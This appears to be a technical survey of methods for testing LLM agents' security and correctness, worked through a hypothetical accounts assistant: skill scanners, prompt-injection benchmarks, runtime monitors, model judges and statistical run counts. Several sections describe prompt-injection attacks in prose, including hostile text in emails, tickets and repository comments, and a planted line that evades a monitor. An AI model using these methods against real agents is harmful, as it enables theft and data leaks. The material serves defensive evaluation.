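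An engineer can write a dataflow summary for read_file, though not for the model, so taint analysis can now continue through a skill's prose. But Zhao and colleagues have to assume that the agent "faithfully executes the skill content it is given", so SCS analyses what an agent would do if it followed the skill as written.

It also depends on recognising which data is sensitive. SCS can classify a well-known credential location as secret, but it may miss confidential data in a file with an uninformative name. The accounts assistant's invoice records could easily be in such a file.

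### What a fixed rule is worth after a model's translation

Zhao and colleagues tested SCS on 117 malicious and 117 benign skills, with five different language models as the translator. Its average accuracy was 85.6%, with a recall of 95.2% and a precision of 80.2%. It caught about 111 of the malicious skills and wrongly flagged about 28 of the benign ones.

They measured the translation's accuracy separately on 400 steps, each from a different, randomly chosen marketplace skill. Two people recorded what a correct translation of each step had to contain and what it had to leave out. Depending on the model, between 92.5% and 94.5% of the translations met every requirement. If each step had an independent 94% chance of a correct translation, a 20-step skill would be translated without error only 29% of the time. Most errors would be harmless because they would affect steps unrelated to an attack,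 but an error in the step that contains the attack could hide it.

The sample also came from ordinary skills, most of which presumably had honest authors. A malicious author can choose wording that misleads the translator, and the 400 steps are weak evidence of how accurately it would translate such wording.

Fixed rules produce the same verdict every time for the same translation, and a reviewer can follow the reported path to see which statement is wrong. But the verdict still depends on the model. With the same rules, recall ranged from 89.7% with Claude Sonnet 4.6 to 98.3% with DeepSeek-R1, and precision from 76.7% with GPT-5.4 to 88.2% with Claude Sonnet 4.6.

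Zhao and colleagues also tested AI-Infra-Guard, a Tencent scanner that relies on a language model to judge the skill. Both scanners had the following accuracy with each model.

| Language model | SCS | AI-Infra-Guard |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | 83.3% | 85.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 88.9% | 88.5% |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 84.6% | 69.7% |
| Qwen3-235B | 86.3% | 86.3% |
| DeepSeek-R1 | 85.0% | 85.9% |
| Average | 85.6% | 83.1% |

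SCS has a higher average than AI-Infra-Guard only because of its results with GPT-OSS-120B. On the other four models, SCS averages 85.9% and AI-Infra-Guard 86.4%. The fixed rules therefore seem to improve accuracy only when the model judges skills badly. SCS is also cheaper to run, since it used about a quarter as many tokens.

Zhao and colleagues then applied SCS to 66,157 skills from ClawHub, the public marketplace for OpenClaw, and it flagged 2,473. The team ran the flagged skills, reviewed the evidence by hand and confirmed 627 as malicious, about one in four of those flagged. They did not check the other 63,684 skills this way, so nobody knows how many malicious ones SCS missed. Two publishers accounted for 552 of the 627, which suggests that most came from a few large campaigns rather than hundreds of separate attackers.

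### Asking a model to judge and repair a skill

*SKILLSECURER* (Mecca, Verna and colleagues, 2026) describes a scanner that uses a language model instead of fixed detection rules. The model receives the complete skill and must support each finding with a quotation from it. The scanner discards any finding whose quotation does not match the skill's content.

One evaluation used 345 skills, each with a known injected flaw, and counted a success only if a finding identified the injected text. This is stricter than counting every flagged skill. Cisco's Skill Scanner, using Claude Sonnet 5, flagged all 165 skills that came from an existing benchmark but identified the injected text in only about 79% of them.

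SkillSecurer found all 345 flaws with Claude Sonnet 5. NVIDIA's SkillSpector found about 99% with the same model, but only between a quarter and a third without a language model. Skill Scanner, also run without a language model, found at most 2.2%. Most of the detections evidently came from the model's reading.

The perfect score probably overstates SkillSecurer's accuracy a little. Mecca and colleagues chose Sonnet 5 because it had already found every flaw in the 165 benchmark skills. They made the other 180 cases by altering skills in which SkillSecurer had found nothing. SkillSecurer found 91.7% of those 180 when it used DeepSeek V4 Pro.

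The team next scanned 954 popular skills from a public catalogue, and SkillSecurer flagged 168 of them (17.6%). Three reviewers examined a sample of 100 findings. A majority confirmed 84, which they judged to be latent weaknesses rather than deliberate attacks. SkillSecurer had produced a complete repair for 75 of the 84, and the reviewers considered 65 of the repairs effective.

Mecca and colleagues also ran five flagged skills with each of six models, placing hostile content in material that the skill normally takes in, such as tickets and web pages. The attack worked in 13 of the 30 runs. It never worked with Claude Sonnet 5, but it worked on four of the five skills with Kimi K3. On one skill, it failed with every model. In some runs, the model described the content as suspicious and then carried out the attack anyway. A correct finding about a skill therefore doesn't establish what a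 particular agent will do with it.

After the repairs, the attack worked in 3 of the 30 runs. In one of these, the repaired skill required the agent to show a warning and wait for the user's consent, but DeepSeek V4 Flash ignored this. In the other two, the repair was a prohibition in the skill's troubleshooting section, and neither model mentioned it before running the forbidden step. A repair in prose works only if the model follows it. Adding "confirm new bank details by telephone" to the accounts assistant's prompt would improve the prompt, but the payment tool would still accept the new account.

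### Why scanners disagree

*ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026) compared the results of three scanners on 67,453 ClawHub skills. VirusTotal combines about 70 antivirus engines and reputation services. A static analyser looks for dangerous patterns in code and text. SkillSpector evaluates what the instructions would have an agent do and with what permissions. Only 468 skills (0.69%) were flagged by all three. Of the skills flagged by at least one scanner, 81.9% were flagged by only one.

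VirusTotal flagged 150 of the 206 skills that the marketplace's automated review had judged malicious, while SkillSpector flagged only 14. But SkillSpector flagged 75.3% of another 25,504 skills that the review had judged merely suspicious. A skill can have malware in a script and harmless instructions, or clean scripts and instructions that give the agent far too much power.

None of these figures measures accuracy. A language model produced nearly all the marketplace's verdicts, and its input included the scanners' results. A scanner's result may therefore match a verdict it helped determine. Koc and colleagues acknowledge this and plan to add human labels to a later version.

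Some of the disagreement is about what counts as a flaw. SkillSecurer flagged 45 of 130 skills that another benchmark listed as normal, and human reviewers upheld 74 of its 87 findings on them. A test of malware detection would count these findings as false alarms, although a company might well want to know about them. Before it picks a scanner, the company with the accounts assistant should therefore decide whether it wants to show that a skill's author is honest or that the skill cannot leak invoice records, since evidence of the first does little to show the second.

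### From a finding to a run

Suspicious agent code may be harmless because an attacker cannot reach it or a guardrail blocks the attack. *AGENTLENS* (Lv, Chen and colleagues, 2026) therefore combines static analysis with execution. It first builds a graph of the agent from its code and configuration. The nodes are components such as tools, memory and the interface to the model, and the edges show which components call or control others or send them data. It then adds suspected weaknesses from public vulnerability reports and its own scan of the code, and records the guardrails that could stop an attack.

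AgentLens searches this graph for paths from places where an attacker could supply text, such as an uploaded file, to sensitive operations, such as running a command. It removes duplicates and can rank the remaining paths, which are still only candidates, so that short ones with severe weaknesses come first.

For each path, a language model writes a test input and a realistic task of up to five turns that includes it. AgentLens runs the agent with its guardrails on and checks whether the run violates a condition that the team set in advance. Security experts then review the result. The team tested five widely used coding agents this way.

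| Agent | Suspected weak points | Candidate paths | Triggered vulnerabilities |
|---|---|---|---|
| Aider | 60 | 19 | 8 |
| MetaGPT | 83 | 12 | 6 |
| Goose | 303 | 12 | 12 |
| Cline | 58 | 16 | 8 |
| Roo-Code | 31 | 11 | 10 |
| Total | 535 | 70 | 44 |

The number of weak points was a poor guide to the number of exploitable flaws. Goose had nearly ten times as many weak points as Roo-Code but only two more triggered vulnerabilities. Of the 26 paths that AgentLens failed to trigger, some may be safe and others may need a better test input or more than five turns.

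Lv and colleagues also compared AgentLens with Agent Audit and AgentFuzz. AgentFuzz looks for chains of function calls that end in a sensitive operation and generates messages to drive the agent along them. On LangFlow, another agent application, AgentLens found 11 confirmed vulnerabilities, AgentFuzz found 3 and Agent Audit found none. On Aider, AgentLens found 8, Agent Audit found 3 and AgentFuzz found none. AgentFuzz had identified 171 call chains in Aider and generated 30 messages, but none of the messages reached its target.

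Agent Audit scored zero on LangFlow but 40 out of 42 on its own benchmark. The benchmark gives credit for marking the right line, whereas Lv and colleagues counted only flaws they confirmed on examination. For example, Agent Audit had reported dummy keys in LangFlow's test files as exposed credentials. The comparison covers only two applications and comes from AgentLens's developers, but it illustrates how much a count of static warnings can mislead.

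In another test, AgentLens found 15 of 20 known vulnerabilities in OpenClaw, with no false alarms. Claude Opus 4.6, working without the graph, found two in each of two attempts and none in a third. Even with the graph and the runs, AgentLens missed a quarter of the vulnerabilities, so a clean report would not show that an agent is free of them.

### Are the real flaws in the harness?

Elad Meged, a founding engineer at the security company Novee, argues that people who watch only the prompt miss the real problem. In 2026 he attacked coding agents from Anthropic, Google and OpenAI in the vendors' own public repositories, using the configurations the vendors ship. In Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets*, he calls prompt injection "just the delivery mechanism" and says the vulnerabilities were in the harness's trust decisions and in how those decisions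 combined. Decisions that are reasonable alone can together expose a secret, as when a harness approves a command because it only reads data and a later stage publishes the command's output by default.

Anthropic patched each flaw Meged reported, but he says he learned from each patch where the new boundary was and where to look next. In Google's harness, a restriction the operator had configured did not apply when the command ran. In OpenAI's, one stage could leave behind data that the next stage treated as trusted. The vendors have issued fixes, according to SC Media's *AI coding tools vulnerable to malicious GitHub issues*, but Novee found similar configurations in more than 100 public repositories.

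Meged's argument means that code review can address many flaws. A reviewer can find a restriction that the code fails to enforce, and an ordinary test can confirm the repair. A reviewer can also trace where the output of an approved command goes next and require a new check at the point of use, as Meged recommends. In the accounts assistant, the payment tool should compare the account with the register when it pays, even if an earlier stage has marked the account as approved. Static analysis can help with this tracing if it follows data across functions and stages, which Agent Audit does not.

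Judging by their descriptions, about half of the 12 AgentLens findings with public vulnerability records are faults that an engineer could fix in ordinary code, such as file access outside the permitted folder or a login code sent without encryption. The rest depend on how the model treats text. For example, misleading comments in a repository redirect the agent, or a hostile coding standard leads it to write unsafe database queries. Better decisions about what to trust could limit the damage, but a coding agent still has to read repositories and write queries.

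The accounts assistant would still have some flaws even if every trust decision in its harness were correct. The company could add code to block duplicate payments once someone had defined what counts as a duplicate. A check for emails that disclose too much, such as one telling Harlow what a competing supplier charges, would be much harder to write, because whether an email discloses too much depends on the recipient, the subject and what the company considers confidential.

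## What counts as correct behaviour when there is no single right output?

To test the accounts assistant, the company needs a way to decide whether each run was acceptable, which software testers call a test oracle. A calculator can serve as the oracle for a function that adds VAT to an invoice, but an email asking Harlow to explain a discrepancy has thousands of acceptable versions, and nobody can list them all.

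Huo and colleagues describe correctness in agents as often "distributional rather than point-valued", meaning that the same request can produce different responses that are equally good. The steps can vary too. The assistant might look up every account before it reads the invoices, or check them one at a time, so a test that required one exact sequence of tool calls would reject many good runs.

Testing only the final answer would be too lenient because it would miss forbidden steps, such as Claude Opus 5's use of curl.

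Testers do not need a list of right answers if they can state a property that every acceptable run must have. For example, they can require that the agent never pay an account that a human has not approved, which leaves it free to choose its wording and its steps. It is difficult to turn such a requirement into something a program can check.

### Checking the final state

The simplest check looks at the environment after the run. The company gives the assistant a simulated bank and mailbox, lets it finish, and has ordinary code confirm that

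for every payment *p* in the bank's records, account(*p*) is in the register of approved accounts.

*AgentDojo* (2024) introduced a widely used benchmark that works this way, with 97 tasks and 629 security test cases. It simulates a bank, a travel-booking service, a Slack workspace, and an office with email and a calendar. Each security test pairs a user's task with an attacker's goal. The benchmark plants the attacker's text where outside text would naturally appear, such as the body of an email, and runs the agent. Code then checks the environment, for example for whether money moved. As *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) notes, using code avoids relying on a language model to judge the outcome. A separate check determines whether the agent completed the user's task.

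The company could not test its payment claim on AgentDojo because the benchmark gives users no way to approve an action. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) found that each of the 6,899 recorded runs it examined contains exactly one user message, which states the task. None of the benchmark's 68 tools handles approvals. The recordings also lack timestamps, so they can't show whether an approval was recent. In 52.5% of the recorded runs of τ-bench, a customer-service benchmark, the user gives explicit permission before the agent changes anything, but τ-bench includes no attacks.

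Some of AgentDojo's checks were wrong. Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, found a task that an agent passed only if the recipient had exactly one new message, so an agent that sent the right message and an extra one failed. In other tasks, the planted text overwrote the bill that the agent was supposed to pay. After they repaired such faults, the same GPT-4o model's task completion under attack rose from 60.9% to 72.2%.

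In 2024, AgentDojo's developers described the benchmark as a challenge for both attackers and defenders. Bhagwatkar and colleagues have since cut the success rate of a standard AgentDojo attack on GPT-4o from 57.7% to zero by using a language model to rewrite each tool result without its suspicious instructions. When they tried stronger attacks on the Slack tasks, including some designed with knowledge of the defence, 30% succeeded. A score of zero on the original attacks is therefore weak evidence of security.

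Researchers still use the AgentDojo environment. The US AI Safety Institute extended it for a joint exercise with its UK counterpart, according to Inspect Evals' *AgentDojo*. *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026) ran 13 models in it, and *AutoDojo* (2026) builds a new benchmark on it and uses the original attack for comparison.

A final state also doesn't show how it came about. If the assistant paid Harlow's new account on Monday, before the finance officer approved the account on Tuesday, a check on Wednesday would find nothing wrong.

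### Checking the order of events

Temporal logic adds operators for time to ordinary logic. According to *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (2026), it has become the dominant specification language for verifying LLM agents. For the accounts assistant, the rule for every account *a* could be

**G**(pay(*a*) → **O** approved(*a*))

**G** means "at every step" and **O** means "now or at some earlier step", so whenever the assistant pays an account, somebody must already have approved that account. Suppose the finance officer approves account 4471, and the assistant pays 4471 and then 9902. The second payment breaks the rule because nobody approved 9902. If the rule omitted *a* and required only that some approval came first, both payments would satisfy it.

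Kekatos and colleagues show how much such rules depend on what the log contains. They replayed recorded AgentDojo runs through MonPoly, an existing program that checks temporal rules against logs. The logs contain no approvals, so a rule requiring approval for every payment flagged every payment. On the banking tasks with GPT-4o, it flagged 79.2% of the successful attacks but also 44% of the runs without an attack.

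A narrower rule raised an alarm only if the payee had not appeared earlier as a sender or recipient in structured account data. It flagged 70% of the successful attacks and 24% of the harmless runs. There were only 25 harmless runs, and false alarms among them fell from 11 to 6. Across 700 harmless banking runs from all the recorded models, the narrower rule removed 75 false alarms.

An attacker can exploit the narrower rule, though. Kekatos and colleagues planted one line that looked like an entry in the account data and named the attacker's account. This cleared 94% of the 403 attack runs that the rule had flagged. They fixed this by recognising an account only if a lookup the agent had actually made returned it. The planted line then cleared none of the runs, and the rule caught as many attacks as before with no more false alarms. An attacker who controlled the tool behind the lookup could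 still defeat the rule. In the accounts assistant, approved(*a*) should likewise depend on the register itself and never on text that resembles a register entry.

The approval may also be older than the run. If the officer approved Harlow's account last month, today's trajectory contains no approval, and a rule based only on the trajectory would block a legitimate payment. *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents* (2025) addresses this by letting rules refer to the current state of a tool, in this case the register.

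Some of these checks do not need a real model. In *Automated structural testing of LLM-based agents*, Kohl, Kruse and colleagues (2026) replace the model with scripted replies and check the recorded steps automatically. A developer could script a call that pays an unapproved account and confirm that the payment tool refuses it. The result is repeatable, but it covers only the harness, not how often the real model would make that call.

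### Allowing a stated failure rate

The company might also want the assistant to ask the finance officer about any email that changes a supplier's bank details. An occasional omission would be tolerable if the payment tool still refused the new account. A behavioural contract can express this by stating what the agent must do and how often it may fail. Bhardwaj writes the basic assertion as

P[*f*(*x*) ⊨ φ] ≥ θ

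where *f*(*x*) is the agent's behaviour on input *x*, φ is the required property and θ is the lowest acceptable probability. For the accounts assistant, φ could be "asks the officer about the change" and θ could be 0.98. A test of the contract can pass, fail or be inconclusive, because a small number of runs may not settle whether the true rate is above 98%.

The contract also has to specify which emails the 98% refers to. A rate measured on ordinary supplier emails doesn't apply to emails a thief has chosen because they work.

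Even a high threshold can be too low for payments. If the assistant makes 500 payments a week and 99.9% of them go to approved accounts, about 26 payments a year still go to unapproved ones. *Towards a Science of AI Agent Reliability* (Rabanser, Kapoor and colleagues, 2026) leaves safety out of its overall reliability score for a similar reason. An agent that behaves safely 99% of the time and causes a catastrophe the other 1% would have a good average. The company would do better to use a contract for the questions to the officer and an absolute rule, enforced in code, for the payments.

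### Comparing two runs

Sometimes a tester cannot tell what the right output is but knows how the outputs for two inputs should be related. This is a metamorphic relation. For the accounts assistant, an irrelevant sentence added to an email must not change who gets the money:

payee(*email*) = payee(*email* + "Our office will be closed on Friday.")

The tester doesn't need to know the correct payee, so a program can generate thousands of such pairs from old emails. That is also the relation's main weakness, because an assistant passes if it pays the thief both times or never pays anybody. The tester can add a relation in which the result has to change. For example, if the tester removes an account from the register, the assistant must stop paying it.

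Random variation complicates the comparison. Suppose the assistant pays the new account in 10% of runs, with or without the extra sentence. One run of each version will then give different results 18% of the time (2 × 0.1 × 0.9), even though the sentence has no effect. The tester therefore has to run each version several times and compare how often the assistant pays the new account.

It also matters whether the tester compares individual cases or averages. Rabanser and colleagues measure robustness to rephrasing by dividing the agent's accuracy on reworded requests by its accuracy on the originals. If rewording makes five tasks fail and five others succeed, the ratio is still a perfect 1. This measure may be fine for judging general reliability, but an attacker needs only one of the five rewordings that cause a failure.

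### What a model judge sees and misses

Any of these checks would be hard to write for a question like whether an email to Harlow reveals too much about a competitor's prices. Developers often give such questions to a second language model, which acts as a judge. The judge receives the user's request, some or all of the trajectory and a set of written criteria, and returns a verdict, often with reasons.

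The faults a judge can detect can depend on how much of the trajectory it receives. In *trajectory-judge*, Mohammadi (2026) built a simulated customer-support desk and produced 100 correct runs and 300 runs with one deliberate fault each. Four of the six kinds of fault, including a refund issued without the required eligibility check, left the final reply unchanged.

A judge that was given only the request and the reply flagged between 34% and 76% of the faults of each of these four kinds. It flagged the matching correct runs just as often, because the text it received was identical in both cases and it could not tell them apart. When Mohammadi gave the same model every step and told it to check each one, it flagged all 200 of these faults and none of the 100 correct runs.

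The step-checking judge caught only 9 of the 50 runs in which the agent followed the procedure but added an invented promise to its reply. Mohammadi used small models, and a stronger one might well catch more of these promises, but no model can detect a fault that doesn't change the text it receives.

Developers usually validate a judge by having people label a sample of runs and comparing those labels with the judge's verdicts. *ASEval* (2026) reports an F1 score of 93.2% for its judge on 200 traces, and 95.5% agreement when the judge and the people sorted the traces into four classes. High agreement can be misleading, because if people find a fault in only 5% of runs, a judge that approves every run agrees with them 95% of the time. F1 doesn't have this problem, but it ignores the runs that the judge correctly approved, so it doesn't show how often the judge raises a false alarm.

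To know how a judge distorts a measured failure rate, the company needs its sensitivity *s*, the share of faulty runs that it flags, and its false-alarm rate *f*, the share of sound runs that it flags. If the true failure rate is π, the judge will on average report

*r* = *s*π + *f*(1 − π)

Suppose the accounts assistant fails in 50 of 1,000 runs, so π is 5%. With the error rates Mohammadi measured, the judges would report the following.

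| Judge | Faulty runs flagged (of 50) | Sound runs flagged (of 950) | Reported failure rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Sees only the reply (*s* = 0.613, *f* = 0.33) | 31 | 314 | 34% |
| Checks each step (*s* = 0.857, *f* = 0) | 43 | 0 | 4.3% |
| Checks each step, if *f* is really 0.036 | 43 | 34 | 7.7% |

The reply-only judge overstates the failure rate almost sevenfold, and only about one in eleven of its flags is correct. It is also nearly useless for comparing versions, because if an update doubled the assistant's true failure rate to 10%, the reported rate would rise only from 34.4% to 35.8%.

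The last row of the table accounts for the small number of correct runs tested. Mohammadi saw no false alarms from the step-checking judge in 100 correct runs, but that result is also consistent with a true rate of up to 3.6%. At 3.6%, nearly half of the judge's flags would be wrong.

Solving the equation for π gives a correction:

π = (*r* − *f*) / (*s* − *f*)

With the reply-only judge, (0.344 − 0.33) / (0.613 − 0.33) gives the true failure rate of 5%. The correction works only if *s* and *f* are still accurate, and they can change even if nobody edits the judge's prompt. When Mohammadi repeated the test on a newer version of the software that runs the model, the reply-only judge flagged 23 of the 100 correct runs instead of 33. With *f* at 23%, the judge would report a failure rate of at most 27% for the accounts assistant, and a company still using the old *f* of 33% would calculate a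 negative failure rate.

Sensitivity also depends on the kinds of fault in the sample. A step-checking judge flagged 44 of 50 runs in which Mohammadi had made the agent stop too early. When he then let a model drive the agent, 13 of 60 runs stopped early without his intervention, and the judge flagged only 6 of them. Thirteen runs are too few for a precise estimate, but the gap is a reason to validate a judge on faults that the agent makes on its own.

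### Measuring how much the tests exercise

Any oracle the company uses will check only the situations the tests create. Code coverage provides little information about an agent, so Bhardwaj proposes five measures to replace it.

- Tool coverage records which tools the tests have used. If no test makes the accounts assistant send an email, that tool is uncovered.
- Path coverage records the routes that the agent has taken, such as paying directly or asking the officer first.
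- State coverage concerns the conditions the agent has been in, for example with or without a saved note about Harlow's new account.
- Boundary coverage concerns limits, such as an invoice for exactly the largest amount that the assistant may pay.
- Model coverage records which language models the developer has tested in the agent.

Tool coverage is easy to calculate because the harness has a list of tools. Path coverage is harder because four tools allow more than a million possible sequences of ten calls (4¹⁰), most of which make no sense. Somebody has to decide which sequences count, and the percentage depends on that decision. *Testing and Evaluation of Agentic AI Systems In Military Command and Control* (2026) describes a more direct way to measure coverage for agent skills, by extracting the rules from a skill's instructions and checking whether the test runs exercise and satisfy each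 one. The company could do the same with its prompt, so that a rule about changed bank details would count as covered only if some test included a change of bank details.

Mutation testing measures whether the tests would notice a fault. The tester makes a small harmful change, called a mutant, and reruns the tests. If the tests fail, the mutant has been "killed". Bhardwaj defines mutations of an agent's prompt, tools, model and context. For example, the company could delete the sentence "ask the finance officer about any change of bank details". If every test still passes, the tester has to find out why. Perhaps no test includes a change of bank details, or perhaps the model asks the officer anyway and the sentence was never needed. Because the agent's behaviour is random, a mutant counts as killed only if the failure rate changes clearly over many runs.

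Evidence from ordinary software favours mutation testing over code coverage as a measure of how well a test suite finds faults. *Who Verifies the Builder?* (Sion and April, 2026) reviews research showing that coverage correlates only weakly with a suite's ability to find faults after controlling for the number of tests. Part of the apparent benefit of coverage arises because larger suites tend to cover more code and also find more faults. Detecting mutants, however, correlates with detecting real faults.

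Nobody seems to have established either relationship for security flaws in agents. Bhardwaj's 7,605 trials cover online shopping, customer support and code generation, and the main results concern how few resources tests need to detect that an agent has become worse. A suitable study would take agents with known security flaws, build many test suites of equal size but different coverage, and see which suites found more of the flaws.

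The result may not be as good as for ordinary code. One email about new bank details covers the tool, the path and the rule, however the assistant handles emails that are worded differently. Deliberate faults may also differ from natural ones. Mohammadi's checker could recognise four of the six kinds of injected fault, but when a model drove the agent, it found only early stopping.

### Readings that nobody tested

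A formal rule can be precise and still leave open what counts as following it. In **G**(pay(*a*) → **O** approved(*a*)), the temporal part has one meaning, but "approved" could have several. Suppose the finance officer approved Harlow's account for a £500 invoice. The rule doesn't specify whether that approval covers a £50,000 invoice, whether it lasts after the officer leaves the company, or whether it counts if the assistant's request didn't mention that the account was new.

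A test suite could easily miss all of this. If every approved payment in the tests is small, recent and properly explained, the assistant passes whichever meaning it applies. The tests are also likely to share the developer's assumptions. Sion and April make this point about software that coding agents write, where the code and its tests can agree with each other and both be wrong if they come from the same interpretation of a specification.

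Sion and April propose that a person approve a list of what the developers must demonstrate before anyone builds the software. Ambiguities stay on that list as open questions instead of being settled silently. In their example, users may read only their own documents, and the open question is whether an administrator may read everyone's.

The study tested independent checking, but not these lists. On three programs with 46 deliberate faults, a model that started afresh from the specification wrote tests that caught more faults than the original developer model's tests. It also exposed ambiguities in the specification. Occasionally it misread the specification and wrote a test that rejected correct behaviour, so someone still has to review the tests. These results are for ordinary programs, and instructions to an agent are often looser than a program's specification.

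Researchers have given less attention to defining correct behaviour than to testing for it. In *Software Engineering for LLM-Based Agents*, Ge, Feng and colleagues (2026) reviewed 355 papers and found that testing accounted for the largest share of contributions and requirements for the smallest.

The company can start by collecting cases in which two reasonable readings of the rule lead to different payments. The finance officer decides each case, and the decision becomes a test. The £50,000 invoice is one such case. The assistant will still meet cases not on the list and have to interpret the rule without guidance, as Claude Opus 5 did when it treated "clean up the batch" as permission to delete 120 jobs.

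## How many runs does a claim about a probabilistic agent need?

Suppose the company runs the accounts assistant on 300 supplier emails, checks every payment against the register and finds no violation. For a probabilistic agent, a limit on the failure rate with a level of confidence is more useful than a developer's usual record that the test passed. The company could state, for example, that "the assistant pays an unapproved account in fewer than 1% of tasks, with 95% confidence". The number of runs determines how low that limit can be.

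### When every run is clean

Let *p* be the probability that the assistant fails on one task. If the runs are independent and *p* stays the same, all *n* runs are clean with probability (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The tester picks a small probability α, usually 5%, and finds the failure rate *u* at which a clean series would have exactly that probability:

(1 − *u*)ⁿ = α, which gives *u* = 1 − α^(1/*n*)

With 300 runs and α = 0.05, *u* is 0.99%. An assistant that failed more often than that would produce 300 clean runs less than 5% of the time, so the company can claim with 95% confidence that the failure rate is below about 1%.

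Taking logarithms gives *n* ln(1 − *u*) = ln α. For small *u*, ln(1 − *u*) is close to −*u*, so *u* is roughly −(ln α)/*n*. This is about 3/*n* for 95% confidence and 4.6/*n* for 99%.

If the assistant handles 100,000 tasks a month, the limits at 95% confidence allow the following.

| Clean runs | Limit on the failure rate | Expected failures a month at that limit |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 95% | 95,000 |
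| 30 | 9.5% | 9,500 |
| 300 | 0.99% | about 1,000 |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 100 |
| 30,000 | 0.01% | 10 |
| 300,000 | 0.001% | 1 |

After 300 clean runs, the company still can't rule out about a thousand wrong payments a month, though the assistant may fail far less often than that, or never. Claiming a failure rate below 1 in 10,000 requires about 30,000 clean runs, and that rate still allows ten wrong payments a month. To claim less than one expected failure a month, the company would have to test the equivalent of three months' work without a failure.

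These figures also assume that the oracle catches every failure. If it catches a share *s* of them, the limit rises to about 3/(*sn*). Mohammadi's judge caught only 6 in 13 failures when the agent stopped early on its own. At that rate, the company would need 65,000 clean verdicts instead of 30,000.

The 95% is a property of the method. It does not mean that this particular assistant has a 95% chance of being below the limit. A statement like that requires Bayesian inference, which starts from a prior, a set of probabilities for the possible failure rates before any testing. If the prior treats all rates from 0 to 100% as equally likely, then after *n* clean runs the next *N* tasks are all clean with probability

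(*n* + 1) / (*n* + *N* + 1)

The chance of a month without a failure is only 23% after 30,000 clean runs and about 50% after 100,000. A different prior would give different answers, and nobody knows the right prior for a new agent. In *Conservative Software Reliability Assessments Using Collections of Bayesian Inference Problems*, Salako and Muhammad (2025) therefore calculate the worst-case probability of failure-free operation over a collection of inference problems, so that the assessment does not depend on one favourable choice.

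### When some runs fail

One failure does not refute the claim that the assistant fails in fewer than 1% of tasks, but the company then needs more runs to support it. At 95% confidence, it needs 299 runs if none fail, 473 if one fails, 628 if two fail, or 773 if three fail.

The company has to choose one of these plans in advance. Suppose it plans 299 runs, sees one failure, continues to 473 and sees no more. An assistant that fails in exactly 1% of tasks would pass this procedure about 7.6% of the time, not 5%, because the company has given it a second chance.

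For requirements that tolerate some failures, testers usually calculate a confidence interval, a range of rates that are reasonably compatible with the results. Bhardwaj uses the Wilson interval. If *p̂* is the share of acceptable runs, its ends are

( *p̂* + *z*²/2*n* ± *z* √( *p̂*(1 − *p̂*)/*n* + *z*²/4*n*² ) ) / (1 + *z*²/*n*)

where *z* is 1.96 for 95% confidence. The simpler textbook interval, *p̂* ± *z*√(*p̂*(1 − *p̂*)/*n*), shrinks to a single point when every run succeeds, as if ten successes proved perfection. The Wilson interval still has some width in that case.

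His testing tool, AgentAssay, compares the interval with the required rate. It returns a pass if the whole interval is at or above that rate, a fail if the whole interval is below it, and an inconclusive verdict otherwise. One example is the contract that requires the assistant to ask the finance officer about at least 98% of changes to bank details.

| Runs | Acceptable runs | 95% interval | Verdict |
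|---|---|---|---|
| 200 | 198 (99%) | 96.4% to 99.7% | Inconclusive |
| 500 | 495 (99%) | 97.7% to 99.6% | Inconclusive |
| 800 | 792 (99%) | 98.0% to 99.5% | Pass |
| 500 | 480 (96%) | 93.9% to 97.4% | Fail |

Proving that an assistant does slightly better than required can therefore take hundreds of runs. AgentAssay sends an inconclusive result to a person, who decides whether to release the agent. Huo and colleagues list statistical checks over repeated runs among the features that agent testing tools still need, so most developers would have to build their own checks.

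### Stopping early

A tester who checks the results after every run and stops when they look good will pass too many bad agents. Abraham Wald's sequential probability ratio test lets the tester check after every run and still control the error rates.

The tester chooses a good and a bad rate of acceptable runs, for example 90% and 80%, and keeps a running score. After each run, the tester divides the probability of the result at the bad rate by its probability at the good rate, and adds the natural logarithm of that ratio to the score. An acceptable run adds ln(0.8/0.9), or −0.118, and a failure adds ln(0.2/0.1), or +0.693, so it takes about six acceptable runs to offset one failure. If the tester accepts a 5% risk of failing a good agent and a 10% risk of passing a bad one, the agent passes when the score reaches ln(0.10/0.95), or −2.25, and fails when it reaches ln(0.90/0.05), or +2.89.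 Testing continues while the score is between those values. An agent with no failures passes after 20 runs.

On average, the test needs about 54 runs if the true rate is 90% or 80%, compared with about 100 for a fixed-size test with the same error rates. (Bhardwaj's worked example gives averages of 52 and 34, but his formulas give about 54 in both cases.) No other test with the same error rates needs fewer runs on average at those two rates. If the true rate is around 85%, the average rises to about 80.

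Sequential testing saves far fewer runs when the company wants to show that failures are very rare. Suppose it wants at most a 5% risk of accepting an assistant that fails once in 10,000 tasks, and at most a 10% risk of rejecting one that fails once in 100,000. If no run fails, the test accepts the assistant after about 32,000 runs, slightly more than the fixed plan requires. The test saves runs when the assistant is bad. For example, an assistant that fails in 1% of tasks would usually be rejected within the first 300 runs.

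### Has an update made the agent worse?

Bhardwaj designed AgentAssay mainly for regression testing, which checks whether a change, such as a new prompt, tool or model, has made an agent worse. He estimates that detecting a drop of ten percentage points takes about 100 runs per scenario, with a 5% risk of a false alarm and a 10% risk of missing the drop.

That figure is about right if the company already knows that the old version succeeds 90% of the time. If it has to measure both versions, it needs more runs. Bhardwaj's own formula for this case is

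*n* = (*z*₁₋α + *z*₁₋β)² × [*p*_b(1 − *p*_b) + *p*_c(1 − *p*_c)] / δ²

where *p*_b and *p*_c are the success rates of the old and new versions, δ is the difference between them, and the two *z* values are 1.645 and 1.282 for these error risks. For 0.90 against 0.80, the result is 8.56 × (0.09 + 0.16) / 0.01, or about 214 runs of each version. Small changes in rare failures are far harder to detect. If an update doubled the assistant's rate of wrong payments from one in 10,000 to two, the same formula gives about 257,000 runs of each version.

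AgentAssay reports a regression only if the difference is statistically significant and the observed drop is at least δ. If δ and the true drop are both ten points, the observed drop will fall below δ about half the time by chance. The rule therefore catches such a regression only about half the time, not the 90% that Bhardwaj claims to prove. A company could avoid this by setting the minimum observed drop well below the drop it wants to detect.

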